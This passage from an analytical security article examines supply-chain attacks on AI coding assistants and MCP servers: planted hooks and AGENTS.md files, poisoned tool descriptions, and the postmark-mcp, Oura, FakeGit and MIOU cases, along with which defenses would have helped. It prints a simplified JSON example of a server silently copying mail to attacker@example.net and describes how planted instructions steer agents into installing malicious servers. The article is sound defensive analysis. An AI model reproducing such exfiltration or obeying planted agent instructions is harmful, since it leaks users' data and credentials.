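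CrowdStrike tried to detect 14 of the malware's behaviors on customers' machines. Nine produced a usable signal, and only two were distinctive enough for an alert that customers would see. The rest looked too much like normal work, since coding assistants also run commands and write configuration files, and release systems routinely publish packages.

The packages themselves were easier to recognize. Endor Labs, the security company that published Raj's analysis, says its scanner flagged them within two to five minutes of publication. They contained a large block of disguised code that unpacked itself when a program loaded the package, and the same author had published several similarly named packages in a short time. Malicious code without these signs would be harder to spot, as the scanner tests in *MalTool* showed.

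### Projects that choose which programs start

The developer doesn't have to choose the server at all. Like Cursor, Claude Code can read a list of MCP servers from a file in the project folder. The file, named `.mcp.json`, might contain this harmless entry:

```jsonc
// Stored with the project and shared through Git
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "weather": {
      "command": "npx",                // fetches and runs an npm package
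      "args": ["weather-mcp@1.2.0"]
    }
  }
}
```

Anyone who can edit a project's MCP configuration file can choose a program to run on their colleagues' machines. A stranger can do the same to a developer who downloads their project. The developer normally has to approve the command before it runs, but a flaw that Check Point found in Cursor (CVE-2025-54136) let someone change the command after it was approved without triggering a new approval request.

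Project files can also start programs without MCP. They can define hooks, which are commands that an assistant runs at set moments, such as the start of a session. They can also define tasks, which are commands that an editor runs, in some cases as soon as someone opens the folder.

The Miasma worm, which spreads using the credentials it steals, used both. Kurmi (2026), in *Miasma Worm Hits Microsoft Again*, traces the attack to the compromised account of a contributor to Microsoft's durabletask project. On 19 May 2026, an attacker used a stolen publishing token to upload three malicious versions of the project's Python package to PyPI. These versions stole credentials for cloud services and more than 90 developer tools.

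On 5 June, the attacker used the same contributor's account to change the project's source repository. The change was dated 2020 and had a message about a routine code edit, but it altered no source code. It added a 4.6-megabyte program for stealing credentials and four files meant to make different developer tools run it.

| Developer tool | Planted file | What starts the program |
|---|---|---|
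| Claude Code | Settings with a hook | A new session in the folder |
| Gemini CLI | Settings with a hook | A new session in the folder |
| Cursor | Rule for the agent | The model follows an instruction to "initialize" the project |
| VS Code | Task | The developer opens the folder |

Only the attack on Cursor depended on the model. In the other three, the application itself starts the hook or task, so a model that always recognized malicious instructions would not have stopped them.

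Hours later, GitHub disabled 73 repositories in four Microsoft organizations within 105 seconds. One of them held the official tool for deploying Azure Functions through GitHub, so customers' automated deployments stopped working. Kurmi documents a malicious change in only one of the 73 repositories, so not all of them were necessarily infected. By Kurmi's count, the wider campaign had infected at least 113 repositories.

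Kurmi warns that copying the repository is safe but opening it is not, which is too strong for Claude Code. The Hacker News (2026) notes that malicious settings in a project trigger a warning asking whether the user trusts the folder. But a worm that takes over a familiar project benefits from earlier trust decisions, since the people most likely to receive the change were the project's own contributors, who had probably trusted the folder long before.

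None of the planted files defined an MCP server. An entry in the project's server list could also have started the same program, subject to the assistant's approval rules. Other attackers have used project files too. Google Cloud describes a malicious VS Code task file that its analysts associate with a known attacker group.

### An instruction file in the Downloads folder

In Miasma, the attacker had to take over a contributor's account. A later case began with a single text file. According to Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable*, published on 22 October 2026, the company's monitoring software stopped a coding agent on a customer's machine from installing `function-color`, a malicious npm package. The researchers traced the request to an `AGENTS.md` file in the Downloads folder, outside any project.

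Developers put an AGENTS.md file in a project to tell coding agents how to work there, and OpenAI's Codex reads it at startup. *A backdoored extension and malicious instruction files in AI coding tools* (2026) describes a planted AGENTS.md that looked like ordinary engineering notes. It told Codex to add the attacker's MCP server to the settings for every project on the machine, then install the package. If Codex complied, it could start the server in other folders even after the user had deleted the file.

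The researchers never found out how the file reached the customer's machine. They point out that a web page can save a file in the Downloads folder without a click, and can set its name and contents. Operating systems make users approve a downloaded program before it runs, but they have no such check for a text file. Codex follows an `AGENTS.md` only in a trusted folder, and Downloads becomes trusted once the user has worked there.

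The researchers then reproduced the attack in an isolated environment. Codex ran the program the file specified in more than 90% of attempts. Some attempts used the attacker's real package, but most used a harmless substitute that opened a calculator.

The researchers also wrote a similar file for Claude Code, though they had not found one on any customer's machine. In about half of the tests, Claude Code changed its settings and connected to the researchers' server instead of Anthropic's, which exposed the user's login token. Since September 2026, Claude Code has also read `AGENTS.md` in folders that lack its own instruction file, according to KIberblick's *AGENTS.md im Downloads-Ordner kapert Agenten* (2026). One planted file could therefore target both assistants.

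The 90% figure applies once the file is in place and the user starts Codex in that folder. How often both conditions hold is less clear. Forever Security reports that about half of its customers run a coding agent in Downloads and that about a quarter of agent sessions open a real browser. But the company sells monitoring for AI agents, so its customers may not be typical. A customer with one such user may also count the same as a customer with hundreds.

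OpenAI and Anthropic could require separate approval before an assistant changes its own settings or registers an MCP server. They could also have it treat the Downloads folder as untrusted, even if the user has worked there before. Forever Security argues that the companies have nothing to patch, because an agent that follows `AGENTS.md` is working as designed, but this understates what they could do. Neither company had responded publicly by 2 November.

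A malicious library can plant the same kind of file. NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* describes a demonstration in which Codex built a program using a library that wrote a new `AGENTS.md`. Codex then added a five-minute delay to the user's program and left the change out of its summary. Adversa AI's *SymJack* shows that an apparently harmless request to copy a file can add a malicious MCP server to an assistant's configuration. The server then starts outside any sandbox at the next restart.

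### What the assistants ask by default

Claude Code has some of the most detailed rules for servers defined by a project. According to Anthropic, these servers don't start until the user opens Claude Code in the project's folder and accepts a trust dialog. Until then, Claude Code ignores any approval of the servers in the project's shared settings, so a downloaded project can't approve its own servers.

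Before version 2.1.207, Claude Code made an exception for a private settings file that developers normally keep out of Git, accepting approvals from it even in a folder the user had never trusted. It now waits for the trust dialog, except in the user's own configuration folder.

Approvals in the user's own settings still apply everywhere, which is convenient for a developer who uses the same servers in many projects. But malware like SANDWORM_MODE writes to the user's own configuration, where a dialog about project folders offers little protection.

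After the user trusts the folder, Claude Code prompts them once about each new project server and saves the answer. Non-interactive runs load project servers without a prompt, according to a guide to these settings published by the company HostTracker. Developers use these runs for unattended jobs. The jobs often have access to publishing tokens, so a malicious entry in the project's server list could do as much damage there as on a laptop.

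Codex relies more on technical limits. According to OpenAI, it runs commands by default without network access and in a sandbox that usually confines them to the current project. An approval policy determines when Codex must ask before exceeding these limits. Users can choose a read-only mode, a mode that allows changes to the project, or a mode that OpenAI's manual calls `danger-full-access`.

Cursor asks before it starts a new or changed project server. VS Code's sandbox for local MCP servers is off by default. Its documentation doesn't cover tasks, which Miasma used to start its program without an MCP server.

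These approvals concern settings and servers, but ordinary project files can also influence an assistant. The AI Now Institute built an attack on Claude Code and Codex that required only a request to assess an outside library's code. The Hacker News describes an attack of this kind that hides its instructions in a README file. Anthropic had issued three patches in six months for attacks through configuration files, but they didn't prevent this attack because opening a README triggers no trust warning.

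Even a careful user can receive a malicious copy of the assistant itself. On 29 October 2026, Cursor's extension marketplace offered a backdoored version of the Claude Code extension for about 11 hours, under Anthropic's verified account. Extensions there update automatically by default, and the hidden code ran as soon as the editor loaded the extension. Cursor estimates that at most 5,000 users were affected. An Anthropic employee said neither the company's systems nor its employees' laptops had been compromised. By 2 November, neither company had explained how the attacker used the account.

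### A comparison of seven MCP clients

In November 2025, Huang, Huang and colleagues tested how seven applications handle poisoned tool descriptions (*Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection*, published March 2026). Four of the applications, Cursor, Cline, Continue and Claude Code, are coding assistants, and Gemini CLI can also serve as one. The other two are Claude Desktop and the agent framework Langflow.

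The researchers set up a malicious server and tried four attacks. One was a version of Invariant Labs' addition tool that asked for private files. Another used a tool that claimed the highest priority so that the assistant would call it first and record what the user had asked. Of the other two, one tried to create a misleading link and the other tried to run a script from the internet. "Partial" means that the attack worked only to some extent or that the user had a chance to notice it.

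| Application | Read private files | Record tool use | Create misleading link | Run remote script |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Desktop | Blocked | Partial | Blocked | Blocked |
| Cursor | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded |
| Cline | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Succeeded |
| Continue | Blocked | Blocked | Partial | Blocked |
| Gemini CLI | Partial | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
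| Claude Code | Partial | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
| Langflow | Partial | Partial | Blocked | Partial |

Cursor did worst by a wide margin. Five of the seven applications, including Cursor, accepted tool descriptions without checking them for suspicious text, and the other two, Cline and Gemini CLI, made limited checks. Claude Desktop and Cline showed all the inputs before a tool call, but users had to scroll sideways to read long ones, so a stolen key could be out of view.

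Huang and colleagues conclude that the choice of application matters more than the choice of model, but their experiment can't establish this because the applications didn't all use the same model. Cursor ran on its default selection of models, Gemini CLI used Gemini 2.5 Pro, and Langflow used an older Claude model than most of the others. Huang and colleagues also attribute several of the blocked attacks to refusals by the model. Shaikh and Montaruli's larger experiment found that the choice of model mattered more than the choice of application.

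Some of the results are also hard to interpret. Claude Code and Gemini CLI were counted as blocking the misleading link, but according to the researchers, this was because they can't create links in a terminal. Cursor and Cline ran the remote script when explicitly told to, so that test partly measures whether they obey the user. Huang and colleagues still name Cline as one of the two most secure applications, even though it ran the script, which is probably the most dangerous of the four attacks.

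All seven applications have had a year of updates since the tests. Claude Code, for example, was at version 2.0.25 then and had reached at least 2.1.284 by November 2026, so the table shouldn't guide anyone's choice of assistant today. It still shows that an application may give the user almost no protection if the model accepts a malicious description.

### What the built-in sandboxes cover

A model can fail to refuse, so a sandbox enforced by the operating system would be a stronger defense, provided it covers the program that does the damage. Claude Code's built-in sandbox limits which files and network addresses shell commands, and any processes they start, can reach. But Anthropic states that Claude's file tools, MCP servers and hooks run outside it.

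The sandbox would therefore not contain a malicious weather server that steals an npm token at launch, or Miasma's hook, which runs when a session starts. It could contain a command that the model runs because of instructions in a README, if the user's settings deny that command access to the keys and to unknown network addresses. On Windows, the sandbox works only inside the Windows Subsystem for Linux. Outside it, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox.

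Anthropic has released the underlying software separately, and developers can also use it to confine MCP servers. Anthropic says it restricts both files and the network because a program with free network access could send out SSH keys, and one with free access to files could change the system to escape the sandbox. Restricting only one may therefore give developers little protection.

Another option is to run the whole assistant in a container or virtual machine, which also confines its hooks and local MCP servers. Anthropic warns that an assistant with network access can still leak any data it can read, and that an assistant with permission to edit the project's code can still damage it.

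OpenAI describes the Codex sandbox as a limit on commands that the model generates. An MCP server that Codex launches from its settings is not one of these commands, so the description gives no reason to expect the server to run inside the sandbox. This matters in the Downloads case because the planted file contained instructions for Codex to add such a server.

Confinement makes coding assistants somewhat less convenient. With the network off, Codex can't download a library needed to test a program unless the user approves an exception or changes the setting. An assistant in a container may not be able to use the developer's saved logins or control a browser on the desktop. Developers can copy their credentials into the container, but then a malicious server inside it can steal them.

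A sandbox can also save time by letting Claude Code run commands without asking about each one. With fewer questions to answer, users may pay more attention to those that remain. But users accustomed to working without interruptions may forget that MCP servers running alongside those commands still have full access to the machine.

### The case for broad access

Developers have good reason to accept much of this exposure. To fix a bug, an assistant has to read the code, run the tests, install libraries and sometimes submit the change for review. An assistant without a shell could only suggest commands for the developer to copy, and many developers would paste them without much thought. CrowdStrike acknowledges that the malware is hard to detect because coding assistants are designed to do whatever the user requests.

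OpenAI concluded that the attack NVIDIA demonstrated isn't significantly riskier than an ordinary compromised library, according to a summary on daily.dev. This is reasonable for NVIDIA's case, since a malicious library running on a developer's machine can usually steal keys without an agent's help. It is less convincing for the file in the Downloads folder, because no malicious program had run there and the file would have been harmless without an agent to follow its instructions.

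An assistant also doesn't need every key on the machine to be useful. It needs the project's code to fix a bug, but rarely needs the token that publishes the finished package. Kurmi recommends replacing long-lived publishing tokens with short-lived credentials that PyPI issues to a build service, and requiring a review before any change enters a project's main branch. Short-lived credentials could have prevented the May attack on durabletask, which used a stolen publishing token. Required reviews could have stopped the June attack, in which the attacker added the files directly.

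These measures move some of the risk to the build service. SANDWORM_MODE contains code that adds a malicious job to a project's automated builds and collects the secrets available there, so the review has to cover build instructions as well as source code. Large companies can usually arrange such a review. A developer who maintains a package alone has no reviewer, but can still keep the publishing token off the machine where the assistant runs.

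## Malicious servers found in use

Since September 2025, security companies have documented at least four cases in which attackers published malicious MCP servers. An email server secretly copied messages, and this was the only one of these attacks that required a model to call a tool. A clone of a health-data server installed a program that steals passwords, and a much larger campaign on GitHub spread the same malware through hundreds of fake AI tools. Most recently, two servers for cryptocurrency traders attacked the user's machine as soon as the host launched them.

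### postmark-mcp

Postmark sends email for other companies' software. It offered an MCP server on GitHub but had never published one on npm, so the name `postmark-mcp` was free there. According to The Hacker News (2025), a developer with 31 other npm packages uploaded a copy of the server under that name on 15 September 2025. Version 1.0.16, released two days later, added one line of code.

That line added a hidden recipient to every email. In this simplified example with invented addresses, the user can see and approve the first message but not the second:

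```jsonc
// What the host sends to the MCP server
{ "to": "client@example.com", "subject": "Invoice", "body": "..." }

// What the MCP server sends to Postmark
{ "to": "client@example.com", "subject": "Invoice", "body": "...",
  "bcc": "attacker@example.net" }
```

The client received the invoice as usual, and the model got a normal reply. The malicious email tool in Hu and colleagues' study works almost the same way.

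The security company Koi found the line after its scanner flagged a change in the package's behavior. When Koi contacted the developer, he deleted the package from npm without replying, but copies that people had already installed kept working. Postmark confirmed that it had no connection with the package. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of flawed and malicious packages, dates from 26 September, nine days after the malicious release.

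Judging by the dates, the package was available for only about two days before it became malicious, though Koi describes a tool that worked flawlessly for 15 versions and became part of developers' daily routine. Its credibility probably came more from Postmark's name, and from working code copied from Postmark, than from its own record.

Koi's estimate of the damage is also shaky. Koi started from 1,500 downloads a week, guessed that 20% were in active use, and estimated that about 300 organizations were affected and 3,000 to 15,000 emails were stolen a day. The Hacker News gives a total of 1,643 downloads, which includes downloads of the harmless versions and presumably some by automated systems. Neither Koi nor Postmark reports how many people had emails stolen.

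### The trojanised Oura server

The Oura ring records its wearer's sleep and other health data. Tomek Korbak, an engineer at OpenAI, wrote an MCP server that lets an assistant read this data. On 5 February 2026, Straiker, a company that sells security for AI agents, published *SmartLoader Clones Oura Ring MCP to Deploy Supply Chain Attack*, which describes a malicious copy of the server.

About three months earlier, several GitHub accounts had made harmless copies of Korbak's project. A month later, a new account published the malicious copy, which listed some of the other accounts as contributors but left out Korbak. The server also appeared on MCP Market, a public registry, and was still there when The Hacker News (2026) reported the case.

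The source code in the repository matched the original, so a developer who read it would have found nothing wrong. The malware was in the downloadable archive, in an extra file that looked like a text resource. Running the download started SmartLoader, a program that fetches other malware. SmartLoader installed StealC, which steals browser passwords, login sessions, cryptocurrency wallets, cloud tokens and SSH keys. It also set itself to run again under names that resembled audio drivers.

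Straiker claims that the attackers created at least five fake accounts to make the project look popular. One of these accounts, punkpeye, seems to belong to a real person. Agentpedia's *Awesome MCP Servers by punkpeye* identifies the owner as Frank Fiegel, who maintains a well-known list of MCP servers. Maintaining such a list would give him ordinary reasons to copy a server. ClaudeLog's *Awesome MCP Servers* shows that the list already had 58,542 GitHub stars in June 2025, months before the alleged network existed.

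A name on a contributor list also proves little. *How I found 10,000 GitHub repositories distributing Trojan malware* (Orchid, 2026) describes a malicious copy of Orchid's own project that listed Orchid as a contributor. The Oura download did contain malware, but Straiker's account of a patiently built network is weaker than it looks, and so is its tentative link to China through another of the five accounts.

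Straiker doesn't explain how it found the server. It says the attack exposed thousands of people but gives no count of downloads or victims.

### FakeGit

In July 2026, Island, which makes a web browser for companies, described a campaign that spread the same two programs on a much larger scale. Island's *AgentBaiting* (2026) counts about 7,600 malicious GitHub repositories from about 6,600 accounts. Around 1,400 of the repositories were related to AI, and more than 800 of those posed as MCP servers or agent skills. The AI-related part of the campaign, which Island calls FakeGit, peaked in April. The Oura server may have been an early part of it, since the malware and methods are similar.

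The repositories were copies of known projects or plausible inventions. One account's name differed from a real developer's by a single character. Another repository supposedly connected assistants to Databricks, a data analysis platform, through 263 tools. Its instructions were to download a ZIP file, unpack it and run the program inside.

The ZIP file contained a launcher, a renamed copy of an ordinary program for running scripts, and a disguised script, but no MCP server. The user started the malware by following the instructions, so no host had to launch it. StealC then looked for passwords and open login sessions on the machine, whether or not the user had given an assistant access to Databricks.

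Island also found more than 600 listings for these fake tools in public registries, including Glama and MCP Market. Some registries reproduced the attackers' instructions, along with the link to the malicious file. Island couldn't tell whether the attackers had submitted the listings or the registries had collected them automatically. If the registries had collected them, attackers could get a fake tool listed just by publishing it on GitHub.

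Island reports 14 million downloads across about 200 repositories. It doesn't say how many were of fake MCP servers, and the three repositories for which it gives individual counts offered other kinds of software. Attackers who can run thousands of accounts can also inflate the count by downloading their own files. The figure therefore doesn't show how many machines the malware infected, or how many of those infections came through MCP.

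### What the agents recommended

Island then tested whether AI agents would find the malicious repositories without a link. It asked Claude Code for a free skill for writing cinematic prompts, with installation instructions. Claude Code searched the web and opened two matching repositories, one harmless and one malicious. It recommended the harmless one, but in one run it also presented the malicious one as an alternative and repeated its instructions, which included clicking past a Windows security warning. In other runs, it detected the malicious repository's suspicious contents and refused to recommend it.

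When Island asked Gemini and ChatGPT for a free MCP server for the retailer Walmart, Gemini's first recommendation was a malicious repository. ChatGPT listed the same repository among three options and called it the best place to start.

In these tests, Island asked only for instructions or a link, and no agent installed anything, so the results don't show what an agent would do if a user told it to set up the server. Coding agents do install servers in ordinary use. Zorz (2026), in *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched*, reports that they install abandoned servers that appeared in their training data. Those servers are outdated, not malicious, but when an agent installs a server by itself, there is no person involved who might notice a strange ZIP file.

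Island doesn't report how many prompts it tried or how often each agent recommended malware, so its examples can't be used to estimate a rate. They do show that the model's choice can matter before the host has any tools to offer. The agents in this test judged a repository by its name and instructions, much as they would later judge a tool by its description.

### MIOU

ThreatRoundup's *Fake MCP Servers on GitHub Rob You* (2026) describes the most recent case, which the application-security company Apiiro reported on 26 November 2026 in *MIOU: Malicious GitHub MCP Servers Install the Beretta Stealer*. Two MCP servers on GitHub were presented as tools for checking a trader's points on Lighter and Aster, two cryptocurrency exchanges that reward active traders. To use one, a trader had to copy it from GitHub and add it to the configuration of a host such as Claude, Cursor or Cline.

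The malware started when the host launched the server, before the agent could call any tool. A wrapper around the program's main function began a hidden background task. In Apiiro's test on Windows, the server installed the libraries it needed and then, about 18 seconds in, downloaded an encrypted program and loaded it into memory. On a later launch this took about seven seconds, according to The Hacker News' *Fake MCP Servers on GitHub Target Claude and Cursor Users* (2026).

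Rejecting every tool call therefore wouldn't have stopped the attack. The host might have shown the launch command and asked for consent, but that command only started the project the trader had just chosen to install. The attack didn't exploit a flaw in the hosts or give the model hidden instructions.

The downloaded program, Beretta, takes data from about 200 browsers, wallets and other applications. A second program monitors the clipboard. When the user copies a cryptocurrency address to make a payment, the program replaces the address with one of 23 that belong to the attackers.

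These addresses received about $49,900 between February and mid-November. Apiiro excluded transfers between the attackers' own wallets from that total, but doesn't present it as a measure of victims' losses. No one can tell how much of it came through the two MCP servers, because the operation had 36 active repositories when Apiiro reported it, most of them offering trading bots and wallet tools. Three other wallets are better evidence that the key theft worked. Each received just enough money to cover transaction fees, and someone emptied it within three minutes.

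The attackers gained trust by making the projects look busy. A bot wrote 26,407 of the 26,511 changes to the code. Of 1,319 accounts that had starred, copied or commented on the repositories, 1,222 looked mass-produced. This activity seems to have influenced GitHub's search, which ranked one of the operation's repositories first in 18 of the 54 searches Apiiro tried.

Oliver Zehentleitner documented an earlier wave of the operation in April, before Apiiro noticed it. ThreatFox (2026), a shared database of malware addresses, lists his finding under StealC. Apiiro disputes that label because Beretta uses different encryption and a different configuration format. GitHub had removed 17 of the repositories by 26 November, but the attackers were still adding new ones two days later.

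### Which controls would have stopped them

Nobody has rerun these attacks against all the proposed defenses, so the answers in the table are judgments based on how each attack worked. The FakeGit column refers to packages like the fake Databricks server.

| Control | postmark-mcp | Oura server | FakeGit | MIOU |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Signature | Yes, if the host required Postmark's own key | Yes, if the host required Korbak's key | Uncertain: works for copies of signed projects, not invented ones | Uncertain: only if the host rejected unknown publishers |
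| Pinning | Only for users who had pinned an earlier version | No, malicious from the first download | No, malicious from the first download | No, malicious from the first launch |
| Description-code check | Probably: the email function had an undeclared recipient | No, the visible code matched the original | Uncertain: the package had no tool to check | Probably not: the hidden code was outside the tools |
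| Scanner | Uncertain: Koi's flagged it, but others might not | Uncertain: only if it opened the archive | Probably, once the file was known | Uncertain: only if it checked the copied repository |
| Approval of each call | No, the call didn't show the extra recipient | No, the malware ran first | No, the malware needed no call | No, the malware ran at launch |
| Sandbox | No, the copy left through Postmark | Only if the user ran the download inside it | Only if the user ran the download inside it | Probably, if the host launched the server inside it |

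A signature does well in the table only on the condition that the host knew whose key to expect, and there was no official npm package to compare `postmark-mcp` with. Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* suggests a simpler remedy, which is to use Postmark's genuine server from GitHub. That works for users who start at the company's own documentation, but it is poor general advice because the other three attacks came from GitHub.

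In *Someone Cloned an Oura Ring MCP Server and Poisoned the Supply Chain*, Stafford (2026) suggests comparing the repository's owner with the author named in the project's files, which would have revealed the mismatch in the Oura server. But Stafford, who is building a verification service for AI tools, concedes that a hash of the source code alone would have missed malware in the release archive. The host therefore has to verify the exact file that the user runs.

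Pinning could have protected few users of `postmark-mcp`. A user who installed and pinned the package on 15 or 16 September would have kept a harmless version, but one who pinned it a day or two later might have kept the malicious one. Pinning would have helped more if the attacker had waited months before releasing the malicious version, as Koi's account suggests.

Many scanners would also have had difficulty detecting the email server's theft. Unlike the tool in Hu and colleagues' example, the server did not contact a second machine. The only sign of theft was an email address in a request to a legitimate service. Comparing the description with the code might have caught this, although DCIChecker reads Python and `postmark-mcp` used JavaScript.

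A sandbox is the best defense against the MIOU servers. In a container without the user's files, Beretta would have found no browser passwords or wallets, and the clipboard program could not have changed what the user copied on the desktop. Restricting network access might also have blocked the download. But the malware targeted Windows, where VS Code's sandbox for MCP servers doesn't work and Claude Code's sandbox doesn't cover MCP servers.

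The Oura and FakeGit downloads show a gap in sandboxing, because a host can sandbox only the servers it launches. If the instructions tell the user to double-click a program first, the malware runs as an ordinary application with all the user's privileges. Island's advice to try new tools on an isolated machine without credentials would cover this case, though few individual developers are likely to do it every time.

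### What known incidents leave out

Somebody noticed each of these four attacks, and each left malicious code that researchers could download and examine. The operator of a remote server could copy every document users send without leaving such evidence, because the copying happens on the operator's own machine. The lack of a similar remote case among the four is therefore weak evidence of how often it happens.

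The counts vary with who searches and what they search for. Hexastrike, another security company, found 109 repositories that spread SmartLoader, according to VPNCentral's *109 fake GitHub repositories spread SmartLoader and StealC malware*, compared with Island's 7,600. Orchid, an independent developer, found about 10,000 by searching for copied projects with a recently added link to a ZIP file. No one has established how much these collections overlap. Orchid waited about six weeks for GitHub to remove two of the repositories, so many others may have stayed online long after someone reported them.

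The figures also don't show what share of MCP servers are malicious. Dividing Island's 800 by Tang and colleagues' count of MCP projects would not give that share, because the 800 include skills, and because many of the fakes, like the Databricks one, contained no server.

Koi, Straiker, Island and Apiiro all sell security products, and Koi and Straiker in particular use their reports to promote them. The malware is still real, and others can check much of what Island and Apiiro found because Island published hashes of the malicious files and Apiiro published detection rules. The companies' claims about scale and motive are harder to check, and news outlets often repeat them. Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*, for example, repeats Koi's figure of 1,500 weekly downloads and its claim that hundreds of developer workflows used the package.

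None of the four companies published a count of confirmed victims. Some victims may not know they were affected, especially those whose emails went to a hidden recipient. Affected companies that do know have little reason to announce it. The evidence is enough to establish how each attack worked, but not to compare MCP servers with other ways of spreading the same malware.

### How many attacks needed the model

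Only `postmark-mcp` needed the model to choose a tool, since it stole emails when agents sent them. The attacker did not need to influence that choice, because the user had installed the server to send email and the model would call it for that purpose.

The other three needed only an installation or a launch. The Oura and FakeGit malware ran when the user opened a download, and the MIOU malware ran when the host started the server. Some npm packages act even earlier, during installation. OSV's *MAL-2026-5479* (2026) describes one that sent out details of the user's machine and had nearly the same name as the official GitHub server. Another, in OSV's *MAL-2026-6922* (2026), posed as a server named `mcp-server-pg` and collected usernames and Git settings. Neither package needed the host to launch a server or a model to read a description.

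None of the reports on the four main cases describes a poisoned tool description, although many experiments have tested them. One reason may be that malware with the user's privileges doesn't need a model, which might refuse or prompt the user for permission. The poisoned descriptions in SANDWORM_MODE show that some attackers are interested in the method anyway.

Part of the difference may be that password stealers are easier to detect, because antivirus companies have years of experience with them and can recognize a program that contacts a known criminal server more easily than a sentence that misleads a model. But Li and Gao searched for suspicious descriptions in 2025 and found few, so the method was probably still rare among publicly listed servers.

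In the FakeGit tests, the models had a different role, advising users on what to install. Filtering every tool description in the host would not have stopped Gemini or ChatGPT from recommending the Walmart repository, because they found it through a web search before the user had connected any server.
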